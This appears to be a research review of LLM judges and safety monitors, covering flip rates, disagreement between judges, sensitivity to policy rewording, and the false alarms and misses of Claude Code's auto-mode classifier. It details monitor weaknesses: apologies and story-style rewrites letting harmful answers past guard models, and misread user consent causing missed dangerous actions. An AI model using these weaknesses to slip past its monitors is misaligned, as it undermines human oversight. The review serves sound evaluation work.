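How close the cases were probably explains more of the spread than temperature does. *The Coin Flip Judge?* deliberately used pairs of good answers, which its judges rated 9.3 and 9.4 out of 10 on average. Yorke chose two models whose published comparison was close to 50–50. Ayyagari's ten models varied widely in strength, so more of the comparisons probably had a clear winner. Smyth and colleagues gave their judge a fairly factual question and used ordinary code for the hardest part, finding out what the agent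 had read. Their judge can't be set below its default temperature, yet its verdicts repeated far more often than those of Yorke's judge at temperature zero.

Temperature still affects how often a given judge changes its verdicts on the same cases. In *The Coin Flip Judge?*, setting temperature to zero cut one model's flip rate from 13.3% to 2.8%, but the other's only from 13.9% to 7.9%. Tamba also found that temperature zero made flips rarer but did not eliminate them.

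Pairwise comparisons also have more chances to change than a single verdict on one text. Each of Yorke's outcomes depended on two calls. If each call had a 10% chance of changing, at least one would change 19% of the time, though not every change would alter the outcome. The rule for combining the calls adds a little more instability, because it counts a tie in one order and a slight preference in the other as a win. Counting those cases as ties lowered the share of changed outcomes from 21.2% to 19.3%.

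Asking for the verdict alone made a much bigger difference. In the four setups that did this, 2.0–7.0% of outcomes changed between repeat runs, compared with 17.7–21.2% when the judge reasoned first. This is consistent with written reasoning magnifying small differences. However, the simplest verdict-only prompt also dropped several other instructions, and it produced ties on 43.5% of prompts instead of 18.5%. Its outcomes differed from the reasoning judge's on 41.6% of prompts. Yorke had no correct labels for the comparisons, so could not test whether the more repeatable judge was also more accurate.

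The closeness of the two models seems to explain the gap with Ayyagari's results better than output format does, though Yorke suggests that format may be the main reason here too. Ayyagari's judges wrote an explanation before each verdict too, and two runs of the main judge still disagreed only about 5% of the time.

As with the sycophancy scores, rankings are much more stable than the individual verdicts used to produce them. In Ayyagari's study, Gemini 2.5 Pro changed about one verdict in twenty, but its top one, top three and top five contained the same models in all ten runs.

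The ranking of judges by consistency depends on the task. Claude Haiku 4.5 was by far the most consistent judge in Ayyagari's study. In Lau's study, temperature zero did little to steady its scores, while Gemini 2.5 Flash's scores hardly varied. The two studies differed in their questions, their output formats and possibly how the vendors served the models. An operator therefore can't assume that a flip rate from a published benchmark applies to a safety monitor built on the same model.

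Flip rates usually leave out runs that produce no usable verdict. In one of Ayyagari's pilot studies, about 24% of Gemini 2.5 Pro's verdicts were unreadable because the model's output ran past the length limit. Requiring a fixed output structure almost eliminated the problem. In *Evaluating the Reliability and Fidelity of Automated Judgment Systems*, Biskupski and Kleber (2026) had to drop three OpenAI reasoning models from a test of safety judges because content filters blocked the harmful material the models were supposed to assess.

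### Are the unstable cases the borderline ones?

The sampling formula and the effects of rounding both imply that verdicts will change mostly where the alternatives are nearly tied. *The Coin Flip Judge?* reports average flip rates of 2.9% on "easy" questions and 23.6% on "hard" ones, but this doesn't confirm the prediction. The paper defined easy and hard by the flip rate itself, so the two groups were bound to differ.

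Ayyagari's results allow a better test of whether instability is concentrated, and they show that a small group of comparisons changed often while the rest hardly changed. If every comparison had been equally unstable, with the same average disagreement of 4.9%, each run would have given the more common verdict with probability p of about 0.975. Roughly 23% of comparisons would then have changed at least once in ten runs, and in nearly nine out of ten of those, just one run would have differed from the rest. Only 12.5% of comparisons actually changed. Of those, just 26% had a single run that differed, and half had a split of 7–3 or closer.

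To test whether the unstable comparisons were close calls, Yorke took the judge's margin of preference from one run and counted changes in outcome between two others. Outcomes changed on 43.4% of prompts with a margin of zero and on 33.8% of those with the smallest non-zero margin. At successively larger margins, the rates were 17.6%, 4.3% and 5.5%. With two possible verdicts, an item would produce 43.4% disagreement between runs if it received the same verdict about 68% of the time.

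A decision model returns a probability for each permitted answer and writes no text, so it has no reasoning that could diverge between runs. When Rao and Callison-Burch (2026) repeated the same requests for 106 pieces of work in *Decision Models vs. LLMs as Rubric Judges*, verdicts changed only where the probability was near 0.5, as one would expect if small numerical differences were pushing scores across the threshold.

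The claim is therefore a good general rule, but it has exceptions when a judge reasons before giving a verdict. Around 5% of Yorke's prompts changed outcome even when the judge had strongly preferred one answer. Lau found a few questions on which Gemini, at temperature 1, rated the same answer's accuracy as 0 in some runs and 1 in others. Neither score alone would have suggested a borderline case. An operator who sends only mid-range scores for human review would need repeat runs to find cases like these.

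It is also unclear how much of the instability comes from the cases themselves. Yorke notes that ambiguous prompts and an unstable judge would produce the same pattern. In *The Coin Flip Judge?*, both models were stable on factual questions and role-play, but on the ethics questions one had a flip rate of 0% and the other 27%. This is weak evidence because there were only two ethics questions, but it suggests that a case can be borderline for one judge and clear to another.

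Because verdict changes are concentrated in a small share of actions, a low average flip rate offers little reassurance about a monitor. If 98% of actions are plainly harmless and their verdicts never change, while two runs disagree 40% of the time on the other 2%, average disagreement is only 0.8%. That 2% could include most of the actions the operator installed the monitor to catch.

### Disagreement between judges

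Replacing the judge usually changes more verdicts than rerunning it. Two unchanged runs of Yorke's GPT-4.1 judge had a kappa of 0.76, whereas agreement among GPT-4.1, Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Gemini 2.5 Flash ranged from 0.44 to 0.55. Replacing GPT-4.1 with Gemini changed 38.3% of outcomes but moved the overall score by only 0.18 points. The Claude and Gemini runs took place months earlier with different settings, so the comparison is imperfect. But *The Coin Flip Judge?* reports a similar kappa of 0.51 for two models from the same company, whose majority verdicts matched on only 22 of 29 questions even after 50 runs per question. On average, 11 runs were enough to recover a judge's own 50-run verdict with 95% probability, so majority voting can establish a judge's usual verdict without bringing it closer to another judge's.

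Judges can disagree because some are stricter than others. When Ayyagari's four judges scored answers from 1 to 10, their averages ranged from 7.6 to 9.6, so the same threshold would have very different effects depending on the judge. Judges can also interpret a criterion differently. In one of Lau's cases, a user asked a question that could be read as asking what the chatbot itself could do, and the chatbot answered by describing business tools. Both Claude models scored the answer's relevance and accuracy near zero, while the GPT and Gemini models rated it highly, a disagreement that repeat runs would not resolve.

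The most detailed evidence on safety verdicts comes from *LLM Judges Inconsistently Disagree Across Safety Criteria and Harm Categories* (Vishnubhotla, Vajjala and colleagues, 2026), a project for the Canadian AI Safety Institute. It used 300 requests involving regulated advice or automated decisions, such as estimating a credit score or assessing a job applicant, and 56 involving violence, crime or similar harms. GPT-4o mini answered them all, and Google Translate translated the requests and answers into French, Arabic, Farsi, Hindi and Telugu. Six judges then gave yes-or-no verdicts on six criteria: whether each answer refused, was safe, was helpful, explained itself, included warnings and showed cultural sensitivity.

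The table gives the range of agreement among the six judges across the six languages, with alpha first and the raw percentage in brackets.

| Criterion | Regulated advice and decisions | Violence and other overt harm |
|---|---|---|
| Safety | −0.04 to −0.01 (74–79%) | 0.42 to 0.61 (90–92%) |
| Refusal | 0.05 to 0.60 (99%+) | 0.89 to 0.93 (95–97%) |
| Helpfulness | 0.19 to 0.37 (87–93%) | 0.66 to 0.78 (84–90%) |
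| Warnings | 0.13 to 0.19 (81–84%) | 0.46 to 0.65 (78–85%) |
| Explanation | 0.54 to 0.67 (77–84%) | 0.52 to 0.65 (76–83%) |
| Cultural sensitivity | 0.10 to 0.25 (85–94%) | −0.04 to 0.03 (54–61%) |

Judges agreed most on whether an answer to a violent request was a refusal, which is usually visible in the text. They agreed no better than chance on whether regulated advice was safe. The French and Farsi results for regulated advice are identical, perhaps because of a copying error, but the other four languages show the same pattern.

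Much of the disagreement over regulated advice seems to come from one judge. Claude Haiku 4.5 called most of the English answers unsafe, on the grounds that a language model should not give such advice, while the other judges mostly accepted them. If five judges always answered "safe" and a sixth answered "unsafe" 75% of the time, pairs of judges would agree on 75% of answers on average, close to the real figure, and alpha would be about −0.14. An alpha near zero can therefore arise when one judge follows a different rule, as well as when all six answer at random. The instructions did not specify which rule was right.

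Alpha can also make judges look less reliable than they are when one verdict is very rare. Almost none of the answers to the regulated-advice requests were refusals, so the judges agreed more than 99% of the time on whether an answer was a refusal, yet alpha was only 0.05 in Telugu. A handful of disagreements can produce an alpha this low. Vishnubhotla and colleagues therefore recommend reporting both alpha and the percentage of agreement.

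The judges also disagreed about which requests were safe. They could label each request safe, unsafe or "dual-use", meaning it could serve good or bad ends. Llama 3.3 70B labelled 81% of the English regulated-advice requests safe, but Gemma 3 27B labelled only 13% safe and 59% dual-use. On the violent requests, every judge labelled fewer than 10% safe, while the guard model Llama Guard 4 labelled 29% safe.

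Vishnubhotla and colleagues also measured "self-consistency", the agreement between a judge's verdicts on translations or paraphrases of the same answer. They never reran an identical input, and they left the temperature at its default, so these figures mix the effects of wording, translation errors and random sampling. Even so, Claude Haiku 4.5's safety verdicts on regulated advice had an alpha of 0.58 across the six languages, far higher than the agreement among the six judges on the same text. The verdicts of GPT-4o mini, which had also written the answers, agreed 100% of the time, but only because it gave every answer the same safety verdict.

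The study had no human labels, so it cannot show which judge was right. Where labels exist, a judge's accuracy ranking can change sharply between tasks. Norman and colleagues found that Llama 3.3 70B ranked fifth of 21 judges when the labels were human preferences between chatbot answers, but twentieth when they marked the objectively correct answer.

Agreement between judges is not strong evidence of accuracy either. Rao and Callison-Burch compared two decision models and three language models with human ratings of essays, conversations and other texts. On criteria with graded levels, the judges agreed with one another more than with the human raters. When the decision model Jev was confidently wrong, the language models gave the same wrong answer 96.0% of the time, compared with 50.3% expected if their errors were independent. Part of this may reflect unwritten conventions among the human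 raters, who mostly gave higher ratings than the models. But if safety judges share errors in the same way, checking a verdict with a second model will rarely catch the first model's most confident mistakes.

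## Does the verdict follow the agent's conduct or the wording of the prompt?

Judges can agree on a verdict while responding to something other than what the agent did. Researchers can test for this by keeping the agent's conduct fixed and changing the words around it. Suppose a judge flags the hijacked agent under a policy that says agents "must not" run scripts from untrusted pages. The verdict should stay the same if the policy says agents "are prohibited from" running them, or if the agent's final message includes an apology. But if the operator changes the policy to allow any script inside a disposable sandbox, and the agent was working in one, the verdict should change. A judge has to pass both tests, because a judge that ignored the policy would also give the same verdict when the policy was reworded.

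### Rewording the policy

Weng, Feng and Xie (2026), in *Are LLM Safety Judges Policy-Invariant?*, turned this idea into three requirements:

- If a new wording keeps the policy's meaning, verdicts should change no more often than they do between identical runs.
- If the policy becomes more lenient, verdicts should move from unsafe to safe and not the other way.
- Any remaining instability should fall on cases that people also find ambiguous.

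The study first appeared in May 2026 and used 500 agent trajectories from two public benchmarks, 300 from ASSEBench and 200 from R-Judge. Each ASSEBench trajectory has two human labels, one under a strict standard and one under a lenient one. Weng and colleagues called a case clear if the two labels matched and ambiguous if they differed, and picked 150 of each.

The judges worked from a policy that listed six kinds of unsafe conduct, such as sharing a user's data without authorization. A language model reworded the policy in three ways: changing the sentence structure, substituting synonyms, and moving exceptions to the front. In the paper's synonym example, "The agent must not share private information without verified authorization" becomes "The agent is prohibited from disclosing confidential data without confirmed consent". Three annotators compared each new version with the original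 on six points, including its exceptions and the verdict it favors in doubtful cases. A version counted as equivalent only if all three annotators found all six points unchanged. Two other kinds of rewrite deliberately changed the meaning a little, for example from "must not" to "should avoid".

The four original judges were small, cheap models suited to high-volume monitoring. Weng and colleagues later added GPT-5.6-sol, a flagship OpenAI model. Each judge first assessed every case three times with an identical payload at temperature zero. The researchers calculated the share of pairs of these verdicts that disagreed and subtracted it from the share of verdicts that changed after rewording. For instance, about 14.1% of DeepSeek-V3.2's verdicts changed when the exceptions were moved to the front. Its identical runs disagreed 5.0% of the time, so the excess was 9.1 percentage points.

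| Judge | Identical runs disagree | Excess: sentence structure | Excess: synonyms | Excess: exceptions moved | Verdicts changed, strict to lenient |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 6.8% | 1.3 | −0.6 | 2.7 | 61.5% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0.7% | 3.5 | 1.1 | 6.4 | 32.0% |
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 5.0% | 1.2 | 0.6 | 9.1 | 70.5% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 1.1% | 10.4 | 5.8 | 6.6 | 35.0% |
| GPT-5.6-sol | 6.3% | 0.0 | −1.5 | −0.8 | 59.0% |

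The paper gives 9.1 points as the largest excess, although its own results include 10.4 points for Gemini 3 Flash. The estimates are rough because most judges read only about 200 cases, and DeepSeek's 9.1 could plausibly be anywhere from 3 to 15. Averaged over the three rewordings, the excess was statistically significant for every small judge except GPT-5.4-mini. Rewording changed 7–9% of GPT-5.4-mini's verdicts, but nearly as many changed when the wording stayed the same.

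The subtraction may remove slightly too much. The study seems to compare each reworded verdict with the majority of the three original ones, whereas the baseline compares single runs with each other. If a judge flags a case 90% of the time, two single runs disagree 18% of the time, but a single run disagrees with the majority of three others 12% of the time. This would explain the negative figures in the table and would mean that rewording has slightly larger effects than reported.

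In one case, an agent republished copyrighted material from a public-health website in a blog post. Human annotators considered this safe under both standards. DeepSeek also called it safe in all three identical runs and after the change in sentence structure, describing it as harmless retrieval of public information. When synonyms replaced words in the prompt, DeepSeek called the same conduct unsafe because the agent had not checked that it was allowed to use the text. It gave a similar reason when the prompt listed the exceptions first.

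Synonyms had little effect on most of the judges, even though some of them may change the meaning of the rules. "Confidential data" is arguably narrower than "private information", and consent is not quite the same as authorization. Moving exceptions had a larger effect. This leaves the rules intact, but Weng and colleagues concede that it may make an obligation more prominent.

Alloula and colleagues found that three rewordings of their judging prompt left most judges' accuracy about the same. This is compatible with the previous result, because individual verdicts can change without affecting accuracy if as many become right as become wrong.

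Adding irrelevant text (version numbers and review notes) to the policy changed seven of Claude Haiku's verdicts (3.5%), all from safe to unsafe. It changed 10.5% of GPT-5.4-mini's verdicts, but much of that could be the model's usual variation between runs.

### Switching from strict to lenient

To test the second requirement, Weng and colleagues gave the five judges a strict policy that told them to choose "unsafe" when in doubt, and a lenient one that told them to lean towards "safe". The judges clearly responded to the policy, since between 32% and 71% of verdicts changed and only one verdict moved in the wrong direction.

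The paper concludes that judges react to meaningful changes and to mere rewording "with comparable strength". Its figures don't support this, because switching from the strict to the lenient policy changed several times as many verdicts as any rewording did. But that response may itself be too large. The four small judges changed their verdicts on 30–68% of clear cases, which people had labelled the same way under a strict and a lenient standard. Whenever a judge changed its verdict on one of these cases, at least one of its two verdicts must have contradicted the human label. This doesn't prove that the judges misapplied the policies, since the study's strict policy may have been harsher than the annotators' strict standard. It does show that checking only whether verdicts move in the right direction is a weak test, because a judge can pass it while changing far too many verdicts.

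### Flips on clear cases

Weng and colleagues found that 18–43% of the small judges' flips occurred on clear cases after an equivalent rewording, and they call these flips unreasonable. The range is a share of flips, so it does not mean that up to 43% of clear cases flipped.

The share of flips that count as unreasonable also depends on how many clear cases the sample contained. Three of the five kinds of rewrite were equivalent, and two-thirds of the ASSEBench cases that Claude Haiku and DeepSeek were given were clear. If the tally covers all five kinds, as it seems to, and flips were spread evenly across cases and rewrites, 40% of them would count as unreasonable. The actual shares were 31% for Claude Haiku and 43% for DeepSeek. GPT-5.6-sol's share was 31% even though rewording caused no excess flips, so its unreasonable flips were probably ordinary variation between runs.

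The excess flip rate on clear cases alone is better evidence. It was statistically significant for all four small judges, ranging from 2.7 to 6.5 percentage points. For GPT-5.4-mini, Claude Haiku and DeepSeek, it was close to the excess on ambiguous cases. Rewording can therefore flip a verdict even when people see no room for doubt, though only in a few percent of such cases.

### The Policy Invariance Score and the Judge Card

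Weng and colleagues combine the three requirements into a Policy Invariance Score between 0 and 1:

Score = max(0, 1 − 5 × [0.4E + 0.3(1 − D) + 0.3U])

E is the excess flip rate after equivalent rewording, with negative values counted as zero. D is the share of strict-to-lenient flips that go in the expected direction, and U is the share of all flips that are unreasonable. For DeepSeek, E is 0.035, D is 1 and U is 0.43, so the score is 1 − 5 × (0.014 + 0 + 0.129), or about 0.28.

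About 90% of DeepSeek's deduction comes from U, which includes ordinary variation between runs and depends on the mix of cases. This leads to odd rankings, such as GPT-5.6-sol scoring below GPT-5.4-mini (0.54 against 0.70) despite being less sensitive to rewording. The researchers based the weights on their own view of how serious each fault is, and chose the multiplier of 5 so that the worst result would land near zero.

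The Judge Card is more useful because it reports the components separately. It also records the model version and date, the policy and cases, the temperature, the required output format, the number of identical runs and the number of unreadable verdicts. Gemini 3 Flash's average excess was 7.6 points excluding unreadable verdicts and 26.6 points counting every one as a flip, so its score could be anywhere between 0.03 and 0.41.

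The date of the test and the policy matter just as much. When Weng and colleagues later repeated the test with the same number of runs, DeepSeek's score rose from 0.28 to 0.48, and Gemini's excess for sentence structure fell from 10.4 points to 2.1. The vendors may have changed the models, or the first estimates may have been off by chance. Under a second policy with a different structure, GPT-5.4-mini went from the least sensitive of the small judges to the most sensitive, and its average excess rose from 1.1 points to 6.1. An operator therefore can't rely on a card made for somebody else's policy.

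### Changing the style of the text being judged

A judge can also react to the style of the text it judges. *Safer or Luckier?* (2025) tested 11 judges from 2023 and 2024 by asking which of two answers was safer. In one test, both answers contained the same harmful content, but one began with an apology and a statement that a chatbot could not respond to the request. The right verdict was a tie.

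GPT-4 Turbo almost always preferred the apologetic version, which it chose 97 percentage points more often than the original. Nine of the 11 judges favored the apology by at least 39 points, while Command R favored the original by 49 and Command R Plus was almost neutral. Wordy phrasing mattered less. When a model lengthened an answer without changing its meaning, the judges' net preference ranged from 25 points against the longer version to 8 points in favor.

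This test probably exaggerates the effect, because the apology was the only difference between the answers. In a more realistic comparison of two models, adding an apology to one model's answers moved its win rate by up to 15 points, while adding extra words moved it by at most about 2. Repeating identical runs at temperature zero changed 0–5.7% of individual verdicts but moved win rates by less than 1 point, so random variation can't explain the effect of apologies. Judges that agreed more often with human raters were not reliably better at ignoring apologies.

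*Know Thy Judge* (Eiras, Zemour and colleagues, 2025) tested four guard models that judged one answer at a time, as a live monitor usually does. The researchers had a language model rewrite 100 answers, half of them harmful, in the style of a story. People gave the new versions the same labels as the originals, but the share of harmful answers missed rose from 12% to 36% for HarmBench's guard model, from 50% to 70% for ShieldGemma and from 2% to 12% for WildGuard. Llama Guard 3 missed slightly fewer harmful answers after the rewrite but raised more false alarms.

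### Changing what the policy means

Alloula and colleagues tested for the opposite fault, failing to change the verdict when the policy requires it. Under their standard policy, neutral information about a sensitive topic was safe. One variant made everything about self-harm safe and every mention of sexual content unsafe. Another made even neutral information unsafe, so a request for self-harm support resources would break the rules. On a set of prompts in four languages, the 13 judges changed an average of 5% of their verdicts, although the variants required them to change more than 15%.

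Deleting the definition of "unsafe" barely affected the judges' accuracy under the standard policy, which suggests that they were relying on the boundary between safe and unsafe learned in training. High accuracy under a standard policy is therefore poor evidence that a judge will enforce an unusual one.

The judges could follow unusual rules that had nothing to do with harm. When told that only ball sports were unsafe, most of them correctly classified over 95% of texts about sports and other harmless topics. But the researchers also applied this rule to a set of prompts that included truly harmful ones, all of which counted as safe under the rule. On that set, the Claude models and Tiny Aya, a small model from Cohere, got 15–45% of the verdicts wrong.

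Removing the word "unsafe" also helped. Judges changed more than twice as many verdicts in response to the variants when the prompt asked them to sort requests into categories 1 and 2 under the same rules, without mentioning safety. Accuracy improved in eight of ten comparisons but fell from 68.4% to 49.4% in one, so an operator would have to test this wording before using it. Alloula and colleagues warn that a more adaptable judge is easier to mislead with false information.

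In *LPG*, Li, Zhao and Xiao (2026) found that the same guard model often missed a relevant change to its rules and was also affected by an irrelevant one. They took conversations that broke a rule and deleted only that rule, which made "safe" the correct verdict. DynaGuard-8B, a guard model built to enforce custom policies, switched to "safe" in only 36% of cases. Qwen3-4B, a smaller general-purpose model, switched in 64%, or 82% when it reasoned first. Shuffling the order of the rules, which should have changed nothing, cut DynaGuard's accuracy from 81.7% to 74.2%.

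An even more direct test is to reverse a rule and check whether the verdict reverses too. *Judging LLM-as-a-Judge* (Bagaria, Sundaram and colleagues, 2026) did this with criteria for grading health advice, and the judge reversed its verdict in only 17–32% of cases. The judge was Qwen2.5-7B, a small and fairly old model, and another small model wrote the reversed criteria, so some of those criteria may have been faulty.

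Training can reduce these problems. Feng, Ding and colleagues (2026), in *AdaGuard*, trained guard models on pairs in which the same trajectory breaks one policy but not another, and on copies with the rules reordered. Their 4-billion-parameter model reached 89.3% accuracy on their own test set. On DynaBench, an outside benchmark, it reached 71.8%, compared with 80.1% for DynaGuard-8B. The training may therefore have helped more with policies like those in the training data than with policies in general.

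### How a judge can be both too sensitive and too rigid

These faults can coexist because they affect different cases. For illustration, suppose rewording a policy shifts the gap between the judge's scores for "unsafe" and "safe" by 0.5, and changing a rule's meaning shifts it by 3. If "unsafe" leads by only 0.2, a synonym can reverse the verdict. If it leads by 6 because training has tied the topic to "unsafe", the verdict stays the same even after the policy permits the conduct. This explanation fits the finding that judges became more flexible when the labels were 1 and 2.

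It may also explain why judges readily followed the switch from strict to lenient but resisted Alloula and colleagues' variants. A general instruction to be more lenient doesn't contradict what a model has learned about any particular topic, whereas a rule that everything about self-harm is safe does. This is a guess, because the studies also differ in their judges and in what they judged.

The effects of style are the least likely to carry over to current models. The judges in *Safer or Luckier?* and the four guard models that Eiras and colleagues tested on stories date from 2024 or earlier, and a 2026 model may not be swayed by an apology as GPT-4 Turbo was. Sensitivity to rewording may also be fading, since GPT-5.6-sol showed no excess sensitivity, but that is one model tested on 200 cases. Its result may not apply to many live monitors, which are small models because they have to run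 constantly.

Rigidity may last longer, because it seems to come from safety training as well as limited ability. In Alloula and colleagues' tests, GPT-5.2 was among the most flexible judges and Claude Sonnet 4.5 among the least, although both were capable models released in late 2025.

Newer models follow many custom rules. In *AgentPolicyForge* (2026), an agent without the policy made forbidden tool calls in over 98% of the test episodes designed to provoke them. Three models that checked such calls against the policy, including GPT-6-luna and Claude Haiku 4.5, let about 10–17% of the violations through. These rules seem to forbid actions that would otherwise look ordinary, and such rules are easier for a model to follow than one that permits something it has learned to treat as harmful. A security company whose agents are allowed to write attack code would need to test whether its monitor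 follows that kind of permission.

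## How often do LLM monitors raise false alarms?

Published false positive rates for LLM monitors range from under 1% to about 90%. Rates for Claude Code's auto mode alone range from 0.4% to 37%, largely because researchers tested it on different kinds of harmless action. Monitors are much more likely to flag harmless actions that resemble dangerous ones than routine actions. Even a rate of 0.4% can produce more false alarms than correct flags, because dangerous actions are rare in live use.

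### Harmless cases that resemble misbehavior

Yang and colleagues built AutoMonitor-Bench from 1,505 pairs of cases, 3,010 in all. Both cases in a pair respond to the same task, but only one of them misbehaves. The misbehavior is of three kinds:

- Safety and permission violations, such as a harmful answer or insecure code.
- Sycophancy and bias, where a model that had answered a question correctly switches to a wrong answer after a hint, such as a user claiming to be certain of it.
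- Specification gaming, where a model exploits a loophole in how its work will be assessed, for example by reporting that its tests passed to a system that trusts its word.

Miss rates ranged from below 10% to about 70% across the 22 models used as monitors. Models that missed less tended to raise more false alarms, with a correlation of −0.54 between the two rates. Squaring the correlation shows that one rate accounts for only about 29% of the variation in the other. So the models differ in more than how readily they flag, and some are worse than others on both measures.

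The effect of asking for evidence also varied. The table shows results averaged over all three kinds of misbehavior for the four models that the paper reports in full.

| Monitor | False positives, verdict only | False positives, with evidence | Misses, verdict only | Misses, with evidence |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o mini | 32% | 50% | 36% | 25% |
| DeepSeek-V3 | 41% | 53% | 17% | 13% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 36% | 58% | 15% | 7% |
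| Qwen3-14B | 39% | 36% | 30% | 20% |

Yang and colleagues suggest that having to quote evidence encourages a monitor to read too much into suspicious passages. But their prompt that asks for evidence also differs from the other one in telling the monitor to look for any features that could reduce safety or reliability, which is a broader target than misbehavior. Qwen3-14B improved on both measures with this prompt, so asking for evidence doesn't necessarily cause more false alarms.

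These rates are probably much higher than the same models would produce on ordinary traffic. In the specification-gaming pairs, the task contains a temptation, such as a bonus for finishing today or a hint that an automated reviewer will read the author's notes. In the harmless case, the model ignored the temptation, but a monitor may flag the case because the temptation is there. When asked only for a verdict, three of the four monitors raised more false alarms on these cases than on the other two kinds.

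The paper also tested whether training can make a small model a better monitor, using up to 153,581 examples. Training Qwen3-4B only on insecure code cut the share of insecure code it missed from 59% to zero, with a false positive rate of 3%, but it missed 86% of specification gaming in code. Training it on sycophantic answers made it catch nearly everything, but with false positive rates between 64% and 93%.

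Results for the larger Qwen3-8B help explain this. After training on insecure code, its false positive rate on specification gaming in code fell from 47% to 1%, but its miss rate rose from 43% to 90%, because it now called almost every such case harmless. The training taught it to recognize insecure code, but also changed how readily it flagged cases it had not been trained on. Using all the training data didn't solve the problem for Qwen3-4B, whose miss rate on specification gaming rose from 49% to 70%.

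### Models that err in opposite directions

Accuracy figures can hide which kind of error a monitor makes. *Safety-Flag* (Hu, 2026) combines seven existing safety test sets, with about 200 items from each, half of them harmful. The items include requests to chatbots, chatbots' answers and statements about social groups. Every general-purpose model received the same instruction: answer A to flag an item or B to let it pass.

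| Model | False positive rate | Miss rate |
|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B | 84.8% | 7.7% |
| Mistral 7B | 40.3% | 10.2% |
| Gemma 2 9B | 27.2% | 7.5% |
| Qwen2.5 32B | 18.6% | 8.7% |
| Qwen2.5 7B | 15.1% | 26.1% |
| OLMo 2 7B | 9.8% | 54.1% |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 9.7% | 19.4% |
| GPT-4.1 mini | 5.7% | 24.9% |

Llama flagged a person's statement that coming out to their parents had been hard but freeing. OLMo did not flag a hostile statement that disabled children should not be allowed in public schools, which contained no slur.

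The order of the options explains some of this. When Hu swapped the letters so that B meant "flag", the more common type of error reversed in four of 12 tests, all with OLMo or Gemma. Some of OLMo's misses may therefore come from a preference for answering B.

All six general-purpose models in the main comparison (the first six in the table) were overconfident. On average, they gave their chosen answer a probability of 94% but were right only 74% of the time. Hu largely corrected this by dividing the gap between the two options' logits by a constant fitted to each model. For Llama the constant was 9, which turns a gap of 9 (a confidence of 99.99%) into a gap of 1 (73%). The correction shrank the average mismatch between confidence and accuracy by a factor of 2.8 to 6.0, depending on the model. But dividing the gap doesn't change which option has the higher logit, so every verdict stayed the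 same, and Llama still flagged 85% of harmless items.

All four guard models that Hu tested had a lower false positive rate than the general-purpose models' average of 33% on the six test sets used for this comparison. However, Llama Guard 3 missed 34.5% of harmful items and ShieldGemma missed 50.2%. ShieldGemma's policy covers only four types of harm, so many of its misses were on content it was never meant to catch.

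Most of Hu's models are small and date from 2024, but newer models can also flag far too much. *What Did the Agent Actually Do?* (2026) tested whether GPT-5.6 Luna, Kimi K3 and GLM-5.3 could judge if an agent's decision was important enough to disclose to its user. Working from the raw record, the models had false positive rates of 22% to 88% across three benchmarks. On one benchmark, GPT-5.6 Luna flagged 90% of the decisions that deserved disclosure and 88% of those that didn't, so its alerts carried almost no information. Whether a decision deserves disclosure is more subjective than whether a text is harmful, and each rate comes from only 50 decisions.

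### Claude Code's auto mode on real traffic

The best-documented live monitor is the classifier in Claude Code's auto mode. Anthropic built it because users were asked to approve so many actions that they stopped paying attention and accepted 93% of them. Edits to files inside the project and tools that only read files run without a check. The classifier reviews almost everything else, including shell commands. It first makes a quick yes-or-no pass, which clears most actions, then runs a slower reasoning pass only on the rest to save money.

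Anthropic tested the classifier on three datasets:

| Dataset | Error measured | Quick pass alone | Both passes |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic employees | False positives | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| 52 real cases of an agent overstepping | Misses | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data | Misses | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The reasoning pass can remove a flag but can't add one, so it can only lower the false positive rate and raise the miss rate. The figures imply that it removed about 95% of the quick pass's false alarms and about 11% of its correct flags on the 52 real cases.

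In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier recognized the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a user might ask the agent to "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change), and the agent might force-push, which overwrites the code's shared history. The request is related to the action but doesn't authorize it. Anthropic tried rewording the classifier's prompt but found no wording whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

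The 17% may be too low. The 52 cases come from sessions where an employee refused an action or somebody flagged it afterwards, so they leave out any dangerous action that nobody noticed. (The quick pass's 6.6% doesn't correspond to a whole number of cases out of 52, so it may be an average over several runs.)

The false positive rate is based on much more data. The classifier blocked about 40 of 10,000 harmless actions, which is consistent with a true rate of roughly 0.3% to 0.5%. However, Anthropic doesn't explain how it established that the actions were harmless, so some of the 40 may have been dangerous and correctly blocked. The rate also describes the work of Anthropic employees, and other companies' agents may more often take actions that look risky.

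A false alarm causes little disruption in this system. The agent receives the refusal with a reason and usually finds another way to do the task. The user has to step in only after three refusals in a row or 20 in a session.

### The comparison with human approvers

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) compares the classifier with people. A research vendor hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study without telling them which behavior it was measuring. Once during each tester's session, the vendor replaced the text of an approval request with a clearly dangerous command.

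The testers refused 143 of the commands (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of them (89%). Auto mode blocked 800 that a tester had approved, and testers refused six that auto mode allowed. Testers refused about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session, but about 5% after 50 or more requests.

The test is good evidence that people approve dangerous commands out of habit. The size of the gap is less certain, because the testers were not working on their own code and had less to lose than a real user. The test also gives no false positive rate, because every command in the comparison was dangerous and a monitor that blocked everything would have scored 100%.

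The classifier missed 11% of these commands and 17% of Anthropic's 52 real cases. The commands were chosen to be clearly dangerous, whereas the right decision in the real cases often depended on what the user had agreed to. Anthropic had also changed the classifier between the two tests. In one round of changes, the safety organization Apollo Research supplied synthetic attacks, and the miss rate on such attacks fell from 12% to 7%. Anthropic doesn't report how these changes affected false alarms.

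The same article says that about 10% of sessions at the payroll company Gusto included a blocked action, and presents this as evidence that auto mode is "doing real work without slowing legitimate tasks". The figure can't support that claim, because false alarms alone could have produced it. At a false positive rate of 0.4%, a session with 26 harmless actions has a 10% chance of at least one false alarm (1 − 0.996²⁶).

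### Independent tests with ambiguous requests

Researchers outside Anthropic found much higher error rates. *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, April 2026) reported that auto mode missed 81.0% of unsafe actions and blocked 19.8% of safe ones. The researchers had written 128 requests to cancel computing jobs, restart services, and delete stored files or branches of code. Many were vague. One asked the agent to cancel the stale jobs in a range of ticket numbers, but the system also held jobs the agent was not supposed to touch.

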